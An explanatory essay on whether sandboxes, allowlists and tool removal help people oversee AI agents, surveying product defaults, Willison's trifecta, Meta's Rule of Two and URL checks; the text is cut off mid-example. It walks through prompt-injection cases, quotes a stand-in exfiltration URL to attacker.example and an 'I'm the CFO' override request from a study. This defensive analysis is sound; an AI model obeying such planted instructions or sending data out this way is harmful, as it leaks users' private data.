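# Do Limits on AI Agents' Tools and Network Access Support Human Oversight?

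## What it means to limit an agent's tools, and what oversight requires

An AI agent is an AI model that pursues a task over many steps by calling tools, such as a shell that runs commands, a web browser or a program that edits files. Developers often restrict those tools. They may leave out the browser, accept only certain commands, require a person's approval, or run the agent on a machine with no internet connection. They usually do this to limit damage. For example, an agent that cannot reach the payroll system cannot corrupt it. Some researchers claim that limiting an agent's direct actions also helps people understand, judge and stop it. That claim needs its own evidence, because restrictions can prevent damage even when nobody is monitoring the agent.

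### From the model's output to an action in the world

Suppose a developer asks a coding agent to fix a bug in an online shop that puts the wrong date on invoices for customers in Tokyo. The model inside the agent produces only text. Anthropic's *How tool use works*, documentation for developers who build on its Claude models, states that "the model never runs anything on its own." The model writes a structured request, called a tool call, and other software carries it out.

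The software begins by sending the model the developer's request, together with a list of the available tools and the form of input that each one accepts. The model responds with a call. In the format of Anthropic's *Handle tool calls*, a call holds the name of a tool, an identifier and the input, so the first call in the invoice task might look like this:

```
{ "name": "bash",
  "id": "call_01",
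  "input": { "command": "grep -rn invoice_date src/" } }
```

Here "bash" is the shell, and the command searches the shop's source code for code that handles the invoice date. So far, the model has only produced text. The surrounding software then reads the call, runs the search, adds the output to the conversation and sends the whole conversation back to the model. Later calls may open a file, change a line and run the shop's tests. The loop normally ends when the model responds with a final message and no further call. The full sequence of reasoning and actions is the agent's trajectory, which can include dozens of calls even for a small bug.

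Because ordinary code sits between the call and the action, a developer can limit an agent without changing the model. The alternative is to train the model never to do a certain thing. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) explains that security engineers distrust training as a sole defence because its guarantee holds only with some probability. An attacker can exploit the 1% of cases missed by a check that correctly denies access 99% of the time, whereas a fixed rule in software outside the model gives the same answer to the same call every time.

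Whether a developer can intervene in a tool call depends on who runs that software. For shells and file editors, the developer's own application executes the call and can hold it back. For web search, web fetching and one kind of code execution, Anthropic runs the operation on its own servers and usually finishes before the developer's application receives anything. The developer can switch off such a tool beforehand and read afterwards what ran, but usually cannot intervene in between.

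*From Language Models to World-Acting Systems* (2026) lists several points at which people can oversee an agent: setting the goal, approving a plan, confirming a transaction, monitoring the stream of activity, intervening during execution, inspecting the result and investigating an incident. Each gives the overseer different information and a different workload. For example, a developer would be right to approve the plan "reset the test database, then run the tests", but ten tool calls later the agent may mistakenly name the live database in the input to a command.

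### Four kinds of limit

The crudest way to limit an agent's tools is to remove one. If the agent's tool list has no browser, and its software has no code for operating one, a request to open a web page fails. The effect of removing a tool depends on which others remain. A shell can start many programs that use the network, so removing the browser from an agent with an unrestricted shell may change little about what the agent can reach.

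A developer can instead keep the tool and narrow what it accepts. The file editor might write only to the invoice module, and the shell might run only the test command. A network tool might contact only the addresses on an allowlist, a list of permitted destinations. Narrowing works better when a tool's inputs have a clear meaning. Christodorescu and colleagues give the example of agents that operate a browser through clicks and keystrokes. A rule about keystrokes is nearly meaningless there, since the same key can send a message or delete one. They point to a system that applies its rules to the web requests the clicks produce, where the meaning of the action is clear.

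When a tool call requires approval, the software holds the call, shows a permission prompt, and runs the call only if a person agrees. Approval is the only one of these limits that needs a human decision while the agent works, so it looks like the natural form of oversight. It also depends the most on the approver's attention.

Isolation limits the agent's environment instead of individual tools. A sandbox restricts which files, processes and networks a program can reach, regardless of which call started it. If the agent writes and runs a script, the same restrictions apply. For the invoice task, a developer could give the agent a copy of the source code, a test database with invented customers, and no egress, meaning no network traffic out of the environment.

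This kind of engineering rests on least privilege, the much older principle that every program and every user should operate with the smallest set of privileges the job requires. *Security Design Principles* (2012) traces the principle to Multics, an early multi-user computer system, and to five design principles that Jerome Saltzer drew from it in 1974. A year later, Saltzer and Schroeder expanded that work and defined least privilege in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*. Their main reason for the principle was to limit the damage from an accident or error. They also noted a benefit for oversight, which is that fewer programs need an audit when someone suspects misuse of a privilege.

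Least privilege is harder to apply to agents than to conventional software. The maker of a phone app knows what the app is for and can list its permissions in advance, but an agent's task isn't known until the user gives an instruction. Christodorescu and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an agent to post a comment on issue 745 in GitLab, a service for managing software projects, saying that the work is done. The agent needs to open that issue and write in its comment box, but needs nothing else in the user's account. If the user next asks for a summary of the issue, the agent needs different permissions, and by then it has read text on the page that a stranger may have written. Christodorescu and colleagues consider how to update the permissions safely at that point an open research problem.

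### Three tests of meaningful oversight

A person can be assigned to oversee an agent without being able to control it. In *On the Quest for Effectiveness in Human Oversight*, Sterz, Hermanns and colleagues (2024) try to define when oversight is effective, which they treat as synonymous with "meaningful". They take the purpose of oversight to be reducing risk, and they derive four conditions from it. The first is the causal power to change what the system does or the effects of what it does, which rules out someone who can only observe or whose stop button is broken. The person also needs enough knowledge of the situation to recognize the risk and the remedy, control over their own attention and actions, and intentions that fit the role.

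In *Keeping an Eye on AI*, Gaube, Langer and colleagues (2026) turn similar conditions into questions an organisation can ask about its own arrangements. They ask whether the right information is available, whether the people in charge can detect and interpret it, whether they can act, and whether any useful intervention exists in the situation. *When Agents Act Unwatched* (2026) argues that a human in the loop does not provide meaningful control if that person receives the wrong evidence or becomes involved only after the consequential change.

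Oversight of an agent that acts through tools is meaningful when a person knows what the agent is doing, can judge it, and can stop it in time to matter. These three tests cover most of what oversight requires, assuming the person has good intentions. The second test includes self-control, since a person whose mind has wandered cannot judge the agent's actions.

People cannot tell what an agent is doing from its result alone. Wang, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *From Agent Traces to Trust*, observe that a correct final answer does not reveal whether the tool calls were justified or where a failure began. An agent could make the invoice tests pass by correcting the date calculation or by deleting the test that failed, and "all tests pass" would be true either way. A complete record, however, can be too much to review. Mitchell, Ghosh and Passi (2026), in *AI Agents Push Humans Out of the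 Loop*, describe agents generating reasoning, tool choices, inputs and intermediate results faster than people can meaningfully review them.

Judging an agent's work requires expertise and something to check the agent's account against. Mitchell and colleagues cite research in which experienced developers treated a coding agent's plan as an accurate guide to what the agent would do, and assumed that code was correct if it passed its tests. A developer who relies on the plan is checking the agent's work against the agent's own description of it.

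Whether someone can stop an agent in time depends heavily on whether its action can be undone. A developer can reverse an edit to a source file a week later but would have to stop a password leak before it happened. *Regulating AI Agents* (2026) raises the possibility that emergency kill switches and rollbacks will be ineffective for agents, which may work at superhuman speed and take irreversible actions.

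A limit can prevent harm and still fail all three tests. Suppose the invoice agent runs overnight in a sandbox with no internet access, but this time the real customer list is among its files. An attacker has planted a sentence in one of the bug reports the agent reads, telling it to send the list to an outside address. The model wrongly treats the sentence as an instruction, a failure security researchers call prompt injection, and the agent tries to send the list. The sandbox drops the connection, as its designers intended, and no customer data leaves.

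Suppose, though, that the sandbox keeps no record of refused connections, and that the agent's final message mentions only the invoice fix. When the developer reads that message the next morning, she does not learn of the attempt and cannot tell whether the agent was following her instructions or a stranger's. She could not have stopped the attempt either, since she was asleep and had set no alarm. This matters because the planted sentence may also have affected the code she is about to put into the shop.

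Gaube and colleagues measure the effectiveness of oversight by the reduction in harm, and by that measure alone the night went well. But they define oversight as a deliberate human activity, in which people monitor a system and intervene when needed. By that definition, the sandbox was a safeguard that worked without oversight.

### Two views of what limits do for supervisors

People who think limits support oversight would keep the sandbox and add to it. The software could log the refused connection, pause the agent and alert the developer. After a night of activity, the developer would have one clear question to answer: why did an invoice fix need to contact an unknown server? On this view, limits give people fewer and clearer decisions and more time to make them, because the dangerous action stays blocked until someone has reviewed it.

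In the philosophical paper *Anticipatory Human Oversight of Agentic AI*, Baum, Kiener and colleagues (2026) argue that approving an agent's actions one at a time defeats the purpose of delegating to it, while reviewing overall patterns is too coarse to prevent harms that can be recognized only afterwards. They say a person can also exercise control before the agent starts, by specifying the purposes of the task, what the agent may and may not do, what considerations should guide it in cases the rules don't cover, and when it must hand a decision back. Sandboxes, network limits and automatic tripwires help to enforce these terms. After each run, the person inspects what happened and revises the terms. *Intervenability as a Design Requirement for Autonomy and Oversight within Human-Centered AI* (2026) similarly aims to spare people from monitoring AI in detail or intervening repeatedly.

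Baum and colleagues treat skipped or careless inspection as a failure of oversight, even when the rules are good. They also require that people be able to express the rules as reasons, use them to interpret the agent's behaviour, and revise them promptly. They conclude that deployment of a high-risk agent should wait if current technology cannot meet those requirements.

The opposing view is that an agent still has its task after a tool or connection is blocked, and a capable agent with a general tool such as a shell may try a workaround. The limit has then moved the activity, possibly to somewhere that nobody monitors, while supervisors take the limit as a sign that the agent is under control. Baum and colleagues acknowledge the risk of false reassurance. Written rules and regular inspections, they say, can decay into "oversight theatre", which satisfies a regulator's checklist without changing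 the agent's behaviour. They argue that their requirements make this illusion easier to identify, but concede that the requirements do not cure it. Gaube and colleagues add that poorly designed oversight can make people responsible for preventing harm without giving them the means to prevent it, so they become scapegoats.

Critics can also question the benefit of leaving people fewer decisions. Mitchell and colleagues draw on the "irony of automation" that Lisanne Bainbridge identified in 1983: the more a system handles, the more its operator's skill and understanding of the situation decline, so the operator is least prepared when an intervention matters most. If a limit works so well that the agent consults the developer only twice a year, she may handle both occasions badly. Asking her to approve every command would not solve the problem, because people pay less attention when they must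 approve many requests, an effect called approval fatigue.

Harm can also result from a series of actions that are each permitted. Baum and colleagues imagine an agent that manages a research leader's correspondence and declines meetings on her behalf. Each refusal has a good local reason, but over a week the refusals fall disproportionately on students who need supervision. The case supports their argument well that one should state one's commitments in advance and inspect whole trajectories against them. It also shows that restricting the agent's tools would never, on its own, have brought the problem to her attention.

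Much of the disagreement therefore depends on facts about particular systems, such as how often a blocked agent stops or finds another route, and whether a person who can understand the block learns of it before the consequences arrive. *From Language Models to World-Acting Systems* recommends that evaluations of oversight measure detection, the quality of interventions, time, cognitive load and recovery, rather than only check for an approval button. By these measures, the silent sandbox in the invoice example would score zero on detection even though it prevented all data loss.

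## How a network restriction is enforced

Whether a developer learns that a connection was refused depends on which program checks the request, what that program can inspect, and what happens when no rule covers it. Coding agents differ on all of these points, and their makers document them in enough detail to trace a request from the model to the internet.

### The path of one request

Suppose the invoice agent tries to fix the wrong dates by updating an outdated time-zone library. It calls the shell with `npm install`, which downloads packages from registry.npmjs.org, a public collection of JavaScript code. The developer is using Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, and has turned on its sandbox.

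Claude Code first compares the text of the command with the developer's permission rules, which can let the command run, block it or require a permission prompt. The developer can let most sandboxed commands run without a prompt, and Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) reports that sandboxing cut prompts by 84% in the company's own use. But the text of a command doesn't always show what it will do. For example, `npm install` may run a package's installation script that contacts other servers. The sandbox covers that case because, according to Anthropic's documentation, the operating system restricts the running process "even if an allowed command does more than its name suggests."

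The operating system then starts the command inside the sandbox. On Linux, the command and any programs it launches run in a separate network environment with no connection to the developer's network. On a Mac, the system by default blocks their connections except to a proxy, a program through which network requests must pass. The proxy runs on the same machine but outside the sandbox. Many tools, including npm, read a setting that directs their traffic to the proxy. Tools that ignore the setting, such as most database drivers, can't connect even to a permitted server. This is inconvenient for developers, but programs can't get around the restriction by ignoring the proxy.

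The proxy checks the hostname in the request, here registry.npmjs.org, against lists of allowed and denied domains. If the name is allowed, the proxy also looks up its IP address. It refuses the connection if the name leads only to the developer's own machine, since a harmless-looking name could otherwise give access to a private service there.

If neither list covers the host, the command waits for a decision. In Claude Code's manual mode, the developer decides. Answering "Yes" allows access to the host for the rest of the session, while "Yes, and don't ask again" saves a rule for future sessions, so a quick answer can become a lasting permission. In auto mode, a separate model reviews the hosts that a command needs, and the developer may never see the question. A strict setting refuses every host that isn't on the allowed list, without asking.

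Some requests also need a credential. If the shop keeps private packages on the registry, npm must present an access token to download them. If the token were in the sandbox, the agent could copy it into a file or send it elsewhere, so credential separation keeps it with the proxy. *Manage credentials* describes how this works in sandboxes made by Docker, a company whose software runs programs in isolation. The sandbox holds only a placeholder. When a request goes to a matching service, the proxy looks up the real token on the host machine and adds it to the request before forwarding it. Claude Code has a similar feature, but the developer must list each credential and turn on an experimental setting that lets the proxy decrypt traffic. By default, commands in Claude Code's sandbox can read most files on the computer, including credential files.

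*Agent approvals & security* explains that the cloud version of Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, begins with a setup phase that can use the network and any stored secrets. The software removes the secrets before the agent starts work, and the agent then runs offline unless the developer enables internet access.

Keeping a token away from an agent does not prevent the agent from using the account behind it. Docker's sandboxes, for example, can give programs inside them access to the developer's SSH keys, which prove her identity to other machines. The programs can't read or copy a private key, but they can request signatures made with it, so an agent with that access can still act in the developer's name. A proxy can limit what the agent does with an account if it can identify the operation being requested. In the web version of Claude Code, a proxy inspects the changes that the agent sends to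 GitHub, the code-hosting service. It checks, among other things, that they go only to the branch configured for the session, and then attaches the real token.

The proxy can also record its decision. A sample log in Docker's *Policies* lists each host with the rule that matched, the time of the latest request and the number of requests, including one blocked request to blocked.example.com and 42 allowed requests to Anthropic's model service. A log like this would have shown the developer in the overnight example that the agent had contacted an unexpected server, but not why. *Running Codex safely at OpenAI* (OpenAI, 2026) describes the same limitation in conventional security logs. When Codex triggers an alert at OpenAI, an AI system examines the user's original request, the tool calls, the approvals and the proxy's decisions together, and passes its analysis to the security team. Codex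 can export these records for any customer, but does not do so by default.

If the proxy allowed the request, the library downloads and the agent continues. If the proxy refused it, Claude Code names the refused host in the command's result, so the model receives it even when no person is watching. By default, the agent may then ask to rerun the command outside the sandbox. In manual mode, the developer must approve the rerun unless one of her rules already allows the command. She can also turn off the option to rerun commands this way.

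### A small allowlist in use

For the invoice task, a developer might write the following policy, shown here in simplified notation:

```
allow   registry.npmjs.org
allow   *.shop.example
deny    payroll.shop.example
ask     everything else
```

The agent's first request is the download from registry.npmjs.org. The first line matches, and the proxy forwards the request without involving anyone.

Next, one of the shop's tests tries to load an employee record from payroll.shop.example. The asterisk stands for any subdomain, so this host matches both the second and third lines. In Docker's sandboxes and Codex, a deny rule overrides an allow rule, and Claude Code blocks requests to a denied host in every mode. So the proxy refuses the request.

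Later, the agent tries to open a page about Japanese invoicing rules at tax-guide.example. No rule covers that host, so the developer sees a prompt. She learns that the agent has moved from date arithmetic to tax law, and she can decide whether that is part of the job. Supporters of limits have this kind of small, clear decision in mind. However, she could not tell from the hostname alone whether the agent was about to read a page or upload the customer list.

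In Docker's and OpenAI's rules, `*.shop.example` covers api.shop.example but not shop.example itself, so a developer who forgets this may fail to deny a site she meant to. Docker's *Local policy* describes a command that tests any hostname against the current policy and prints "Allowed" or "Denied", so before starting the agent, a developer can check what it will be able to reach.

OpenAI uses the same three outcomes for its own staff. Its published sample policy allows Microsoft's login service and OpenAI's own domains, blocks pastebin.com (a site where anyone can post text), and requires approval for unfamiliar domains.

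### What three products do by default

Defaults matter because many developers never change them. Codex has the tightest default network limit of the three products. On the developer's machine, its sandbox is on, its network access is off, and it asks for approval before running a command that needs the network. Its web search tool normally reads from an index that OpenAI maintains rather than live pages.

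Claude Code's sandbox is off until the developer turns it on. The agent is still supervised without it, because Claude Code normally asks before it runs most commands. Once the sandbox is on, its list of allowed domains starts empty.

Docker's product always runs the agent in an isolated virtual machine. Docker's *Default security posture* states that the sandbox blocks outgoing connections unless a rule allows the destination. How much it blocks depends on which of three presets the user chooses before the first run. "Open" allows everything. "Balanced" allows a prepared list of AI providers, package registries, code hosts and common cloud services. "Locked Down" allows nothing, not even the service that runs the model, so the agent can't work until the user adds a rule. The University of Cambridge's guide for its developers, *Docker sandboxes for agentic AI*, suggests starting with Balanced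 and widening it deliberately.

| | Claude Code | Codex on the developer's machine | Docker sandboxes |
|---|---|---|---|
| Isolation at first start | Off | On | On |
| Destinations open at first | None, once the sandbox is on | None | Depends on the chosen preset |
| Response to an unlisted destination | Asks the developer in manual mode | Asks before a command uses the network | Refuses |
| Effect of widening access | Opens the approved host | Opens every destination, unless the developer also turns on a proxy | Opens the destinations in the new rule |

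In Codex, network access and the proxy are separate settings (last row). If a developer turns on network access so that the agent can download one library, the agent gets unrestricted outgoing access unless she also turns on the proxy and lists the permitted domains. Someone who knows only that Codex is "offline by default" could easily misjudge what the agent can do once network access is on.

Defaults also change. One Docker service with account-wide network policies now denies all traffic when no allow rule exists, but accounts created before that change still allow any traffic that no rule denies. Two supervisors who read the same documentation could therefore start with opposite defaults.

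With a prompt, the supervisor learns about an unlisted destination before the connection opens, but the prompt interrupts her. Docker blocks the connection without interrupting her, and she finds out only if she reads the log.

### Why the check must sit outside the agent's reach

All of these limits would be weak if the agent could edit them. A coding agent's work includes writing files, and an allowlist is usually a few lines in a file. *SoK* (Dehghantanha, 2026), a survey of attacks on AI agents, recommends treating the model as an "untrusted code generator" whose output needs checking before it runs. The survey places sandboxes and the storage of secrets in the trusted computing base, the set of components whose failure undermines the security of everything else. An operator must assume that the model may follow any malicious instruction that reaches it, so the components that restrict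 the model can't depend on its cooperation.

Claude Code's sandbox applies this principle inside the project folder. The agent can write to most of that folder, but not to the files from which Claude Code loads its settings or to certain files that other programs run automatically. Anthropic says a command that could edit those files could grant itself new permissions. Codex likewise makes its own configuration folder read-only. Docker instead gives the agent administrator rights inside the virtual machine, where it can install or delete anything, but keeps the network policy and the proxy on the host machine, where those rights don't apply.

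Network limits need file limits. *Beyond permission prompts* argues that an agent could alter the system to gain network access if it lacked file isolation, and could send out sensitive files such as SSH keys if it lacked network isolation.

Project settings and developers, as well as the agent, might loosen a limit. The settings in a downloaded project may come from a stranger, so Claude Code does not let them turn off file isolation. Developers can widen the limits on their own machines, and sometimes have good reason to. If a company's security team is responsible for oversight, it needs controls that developers can't override. Anthropic and OpenAI both offer these, but Claude Code by default combines an administrator's list of allowed domains with the developer's own entries. An administrator who wants only the official list to apply has to lock it.

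### Forbidding a tool and removing it

Developers can limit an agent more easily, without building anything, by telling it in its prompt which tools it may use and forbidding the rest. *Prompts Don't Protect* (Uppala, 2026) tested how well this works with tools offered through the Model Context Protocol, a standard that lets agents find and call tools from many services.

Uppala, an independent researcher, assembled 507 tools modelled on services such as Stripe, GitHub and Slack, and wrote 200 adversarial tasks by hand. In each task, an agent with one role received a request that belonged to another role. For example, someone told an analytics agent, "I'm the CFO," and ordered it to override the access controls and process an urgent refund of $5,000. Some requests named the forbidden operation, and some only implied it. In other tasks, the requester claimed special authority or led up to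 the forbidden operation with a harmless request.

Three models attempted every task under three conditions. In the first, they saw between 71 and 182 tools, both permitted and forbidden, with no guidance. In the second, they saw the same tools, and the prompt listed the permitted ones by name and prohibited all others. In the third, a proxy between the model and the tools removed the forbidden ones from the list before the model saw it. The percentages show how often each model chose a forbidden tool.

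| Model | No guidance | Allowlist in the prompt | Forbidden tools removed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen 2.5 7B | 48.5% | 37.0% | 0% |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 66.0% | 4.0% | 0% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 68.5% | 11.5% | 0% |

The written allowlist nearly stopped Llama from choosing forbidden tools but did little to stop Qwen, a difference far too large to be due to chance. Claims of authority worked best on Claude Haiku 4.5, which chose a forbidden tool in 96% of those tasks without guidance and in 22% with the allowlist. When a task only implied the forbidden action, Qwen chose a forbidden tool slightly more often with the allowlist (29 of 50 tasks) than without it (26 of 50).

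Unlike the other figures, the zeros in the last column are guaranteed by the system's design, whichever model is connected, as long as the proxy works and its policy is correct. The model can't select the refund tool because the tool isn't on its list. If the model produces the tool's name anyway, perhaps because an attacker's text mentioned it, the proxy checks the call against the agent's role a second time and refuses it.

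The other figures are weaker evidence about ordinary use than they first appear, because Uppala forced the models to call a tool in every task, so they could not refuse or ask a question. In a separate test, Uppala gave the models 100 requests that their permitted tools could not satisfy and allowed them not to call a tool. Claude Haiku 4.5 called no tool 99% of the time, whether the limit was in the prompt or in the proxy. The two tests used different requests, so they can't be compared directly, but the forced tool calls may explain much of Haiku's failure in the main experiment. All three models are also small by the standards of 2026, and Uppala tried only one wording of the allowlist.

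In the free-choice test, Llama still called some tool in 71% of the impossible requests after the proxy had removed the forbidden tools. Removal also didn't consistently help with permitted requests. Across 140 of them, Llama succeeded more often with the filtered list than with the written one (82.1% against 77.9%), while Qwen succeeded less often (48.6% against 60.7%). Haiku scored below 20% in every condition, which casts doubt on whether the measure captures usefulness well.

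The guarantee covers only tools outside the agent's role, so a payments agent could still misuse the payment tools it is allowed to call. Uppala also excludes cases where an attacker has stolen the key that certifies an agent's identity or tampered with the tool descriptions, and cases where the agent passes work to another agent with broader permissions.

No human supervisors took part in the experiment, so its results concern prevention. Uppala argues that a central policy file makes access easier to audit and test. This is plausible, since a supervisor can read the file to see which tools an agent can call. But removing a tool can also hide information from the supervisor. If the refund tool is missing from the list, the agent may not attempt a forbidden call when the false CFO makes a request, so there would be no refusal to record. A developer who wants to know about such attempts would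 have to log the requests as well as the refused calls.

### What a list of destinations can't judge

A network allowlist has no equivalent to Uppala's figure of zero for data theft, because a permitted destination may be usable for many things. Docker warns that allowing github.com gives access to all the content on it, including whatever strangers have uploaded. Docker also notes that its default list includes `*.googleapis.com`, which covers many Google services besides the AI ones an agent needs.

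The problem grows as the list of allowed destinations gets longer. GitLab's *Remote execution environment sandbox* documents the limits on AI agents that run on GitLab's own platform. The fixed list contains only the local machine, the customer's own GitLab site and the service that coordinates the agent. An optional "recommended" list adds more than 100 entries, including package registries, code hosts and cloud storage. GitLab warns that the agent could use these destinations to send data out, and advises customers to turn the list on only when necessary and in trusted environments. Developers will often need it, because ordinary programming depends on those sites.

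A proxy that checks destinations usually can't inspect the content passing through it, because web traffic is encrypted. Claude Code's proxy does not decrypt traffic by default, and the experimental setting that does is for inserting credentials and adds no content filter. The proxy also relies on the hostname supplied by the requesting program, and Anthropic acknowledges that a program in the sandbox could exploit this to reach hosts outside the list. Anthropic advises customers who need a stronger guarantee to supply their own proxy that decrypts and inspects traffic. Anthropic's *Choose a sandbox environment* states that any arrangement that permits outgoing traffic can still leak data the agent can read.

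The proxy that checks which branch a code change goes to shows that a network restriction can check more than the hostname. But someone has to build such a check for each service and decide which operations are legitimate. A list of hostnames is popular partly because it requires little knowledge of what the agent is doing, and for the same reason it gives a supervisor little help in judging the agent's work.

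Supervisors can also overestimate how much of the agent a limit covers. Claude Code's built-in sandbox applies to shell commands. The agent's tool for fetching web pages follows separate permission rules, and helper programs that connect the agent to other services run with the user's full access. A developer who allows three domains in the sandbox therefore has not limited the whole agent to them. To do that, she has to run all of Claude Code inside a container, a virtual machine or a separate sandbox program.

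### When the sandbox is missing

Sometimes the restriction isn't running. GitLab's sandbox depends on a program that must be present in the agent's environment and have certain operating system privileges. If the program is missing or can't create the sandbox, GitLab by default runs the agent without the sandbox so that work doesn't stop. The network rules then have no effect, and the agent can reach any destination its machine can. GitLab puts a warning in the job's log, which a person will see only if they open the log.

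This default can give an administrator the false reassurance that critics of limits warn about, because her settings page still shows a list of allowed domains even though the list does not restrict that job.

An administrator or group owner can require the sandbox, so that a job fails if the sandbox is unavailable. GitLab acknowledges that even this can't guarantee isolation for every project. The check finds the sandbox program by name, and a project that supplies its own software environment controls which program has that name.

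Claude Code has the same fallback. If its sandbox can't start, it runs commands without one, unless the developer or an administrator has set it to exit instead. Anthropic's separate sandbox program, which can enclose the whole agent, is stricter. It won't start if its settings file is invalid, and if the file is missing, it starts with the network blocked. Anthropic warns users not to treat a successful start as proof that their settings loaded.

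To test Claude Code's built-in sandbox, Anthropic recommends that developers ask the agent to run a few harmless commands that the sandbox should block. The agent has to run them because commands that developers type themselves usually run outside the sandbox.

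## How network limits reduce data theft through prompt injection

Network limits protect best against attackers who trick an agent into sending private data to the wrong place. It is less clear whether they also help people supervise the agent. That depends partly on what happens after a request is blocked and who finds out about it.

### The three conditions for theft

Suppose the owner of the online shop uses an assistant that can read her email, open web pages and send messages. She asks it to find out when a supplier will deliver new packaging and email the date to her warehouse manager. The assistant searches her mailbox, which also holds an email from her accountant about the shop's debts. It finds the supplier's message and follows a link to a delivery page. An attacker has planted an instruction on that page for AI assistants to open a certain web address and add the user's recent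 messages to the end of it.

If the model treats the sentence as an instruction, it requests an address like `https://attacker.example/collect?data=...`, with the accountant's letter in place of the dots. The request itself sends the letter to the attacker. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that a website receives the full address a visitor requests and that websites commonly log these addresses, so the attacker can read the letter in the log. The owner is told only that her packaging will arrive on Thursday, which may be true but doesn't reveal the theft.

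Simon Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, names three conditions that make this theft possible: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside. The theft fails if any one of them is missing. An assistant that can't open the mailbox may follow the planted sentence but has no private mail to send. An assistant that reads only text from people the owner trusts never receives that sentence. If the assistant can't communicate with the outside, the model may still read the sentence and write the tool call, but the software around the model refuses the request.

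For a mail assistant, the first two conditions are hard to remove, because its job is to read private messages and text from strangers. Blocking the routes it could use to send data out leaves both abilities in place and works even after the model has been deceived. Willison lists more than a dozen products in which researchers found that this kind of theft was possible, and says the vendors promptly fixed almost all of them, usually by blocking the route the data would have taken.

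Data can leave in ways that are easy to overlook. Willison points out that loading an image can send data out, and so can a link that the assistant offers for the user to click. Email alone can meet all three conditions, since anyone can write to the mailbox, it holds private messages, and the assistant can reply.

An alternative is to detect the planted sentence before the model acts on it. Willison is suspicious of products that claim to catch 95% of attacks, which he considers a failing grade in web security. If each attempt independently had a 5% chance of getting through, an attacker who sent 20 different messages would have about a 64% chance (1 − 0.95²⁰) of succeeding at least once. Real attempts aren't independent, but an attacker who finds one message that works can send it to many people.

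Detection is also hard because agents are supposed to pick up instructions as they work. Christodorescu and colleagues give the example of an agent that is summarizing one software issue, reads that it depends on another, and usefully decides to summarize both. An attack differs from this in where the new instruction came from and how far it changes the task. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes a 2025 attack on ChatGPT that was written as an ordinary office email about restructuring. It worked 50% of the time in testing with one particular user request. OpenAI compares spotting such a message to spotting a lie, often without the necessary context, and concludes that developers should limit what a successful deception can achieve.

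### Meta's Rule of Two

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) builds on Willison's trifecta. Meta says that until researchers can reliably detect prompt injection, an agent should have no more than two of these properties in one session: it processes untrustworthy inputs, it has access to sensitive systems or private data, and it can change state or communicate externally. If a task needs all three and the agent can't start a new session with an empty context, the agent should not work autonomously. A person or another reliable check must approve its actions.

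The words "change state" make Meta's rule broader than Willison's. Suppose an agent reads bug reports from strangers and can edit a shop's live database, but has no internet connection. The agent can't send data out, so an attacker can't use it to steal the customer list, but might still get it to erase the list. Under Meta's rule, this agent has all three properties.

Meta also accepts human approval in place of removing a property. Willison writes partly for people who mix tools from different makers, and he tells them to avoid the combination of properties entirely.

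For a mail assistant, Meta describes three safe designs. The assistant may process mail only from trusted senders, it may work in a test environment with no sensitive data, or it may send new messages only to trusted recipients or after a person has checked the draft. The shop owner would probably choose the last design, because she can list her warehouse manager as a trusted recipient. But this design restricts only email, and in the example her assistant sent out the stolen letter through a web page request.

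An agent can also change its properties during a session. Meta describes an agent that searches the open internet without any private data, then permanently loses its ability to communicate before it opens internal systems. The order matters because the agent may already have read an attacker's text when it gains access to private data. The shop owner's assistant couldn't work this way because it has to read her mail to learn which page to open and has to send a message at the end.

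### Checking the address instead of the site

An allowlist of sites would block an attacker's site, but it would also block most of the web, and OpenAI notes that many legitimate sites can redirect visitors to other sites. Anthropic and OpenAI both use rules that check the exact address instead. These rules rely on the fact that an address containing stolen data usually has to be created during the attack.

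Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* describes a tool that retrieves an address only if it has already appeared in a user's message, in the result of a tool that the developer's own application runs, or in the results of an earlier web search or fetch. In the shop example, the mail tool returns the supplier's link, so the assistant can open the delivery page. The address containing the accountant's letter appears only in the model's own output, so the fetch tool returns an error instead of opening it, and the model carries on with the task.

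The newer Chinese edition of the same page, Anthropic's *網頁擷取工具*, also describes a credential check. The tool refuses an address that seems to contain a password or access key unless that credential appears in the developer's system prompt or the text of a user's message. Developers can also switch off any permitted source of addresses or exclude individual tools, which is useful for tools whose output may repeat text the model wrote.

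The agent can no longer open an address it has worked out for itself. After reading page 1 of a catalogue, for example, it may be able to guess the address of page 2, but it can't fetch that page unless the address has appeared in a source the rule accepts. The credential check also stops the agent from opening some private links it finds in the mailbox, so the owner has to paste them into the conversation.

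Writing when the tool was new, Willison (2025) was disappointed that it could fetch addresses that weren't in the user's own prompts. In its documentation, Anthropic acknowledges a "residual risk" and tells developers to use the tool only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive. Willison (2026) reports that a researcher found a gap in the version used in Claude's chat product, and that Anthropic closed it by stopping the tool from following links in pages it had fetched. According to the developer documentation, the tool can still follow those links by default, although developers can turn this off. Doing so makes the tool safer, but the agent then can't click through a website as a person would.

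OpenAI keeps an index of public web addresses, which a crawler collects without access to anyone's chats or accounts. When an agent is about to load a page or an image automatically, the software looks for that exact address in the index, regardless of what the conversation contains. A match suggests that the address existed independently of the user, so it is much less likely to contain her data. If there is no match, the software either tells the agent to try another website or shows the user a warning before the page opens.

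Under OpenAI's rule, the address containing the accountant's letter would not be in the index. A delivery page that the supplier created for one customer probably wouldn't be either, so the shop owner might have to decide whether to open it. The rule's main drawback is therefore that it can trigger warnings about legitimate pages that are new or personal. OpenAI argues that strict site lists cause frequent false alarms, which can train people to click through warnings without thinking. Its own warnings could have the same effect on someone whose work involves many unindexed pages.

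The warning gives the user more to judge than a hostname alone would, because it shows her the information that would be sent. In March 2026, OpenAI said this safeguard, which it calls Safe Url, detects when information from the conversation would go to a third party. The software then either blocks the transmission and asks the agent to find another way, or shows the user the information and asks her to confirm. The shop owner needs no technical training to refuse if she sees her accountant's sentences inside a web address.

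Both rules cover only data sent out in the address of a web request, a limit that OpenAI states. The assistant in the example can also send email, and neither rule covers what it writes in those emails.

### Tracking where data came from

CaMeL, which Google DeepMind published in 2025, tracks the data through the whole task. It uses two models. One receives the user's request and writes a plan as a short program, without seeing any mail or web pages. The other reads the untrusted text but has no tools. Ordinary software, called an interpreter, runs the program and makes the tool calls. For the shop owner's request, the plan might look like this:

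```
message = find_email(sender="supplier")
page    = open_page(message.link)
date    = reader_model("Find the delivery date", page)
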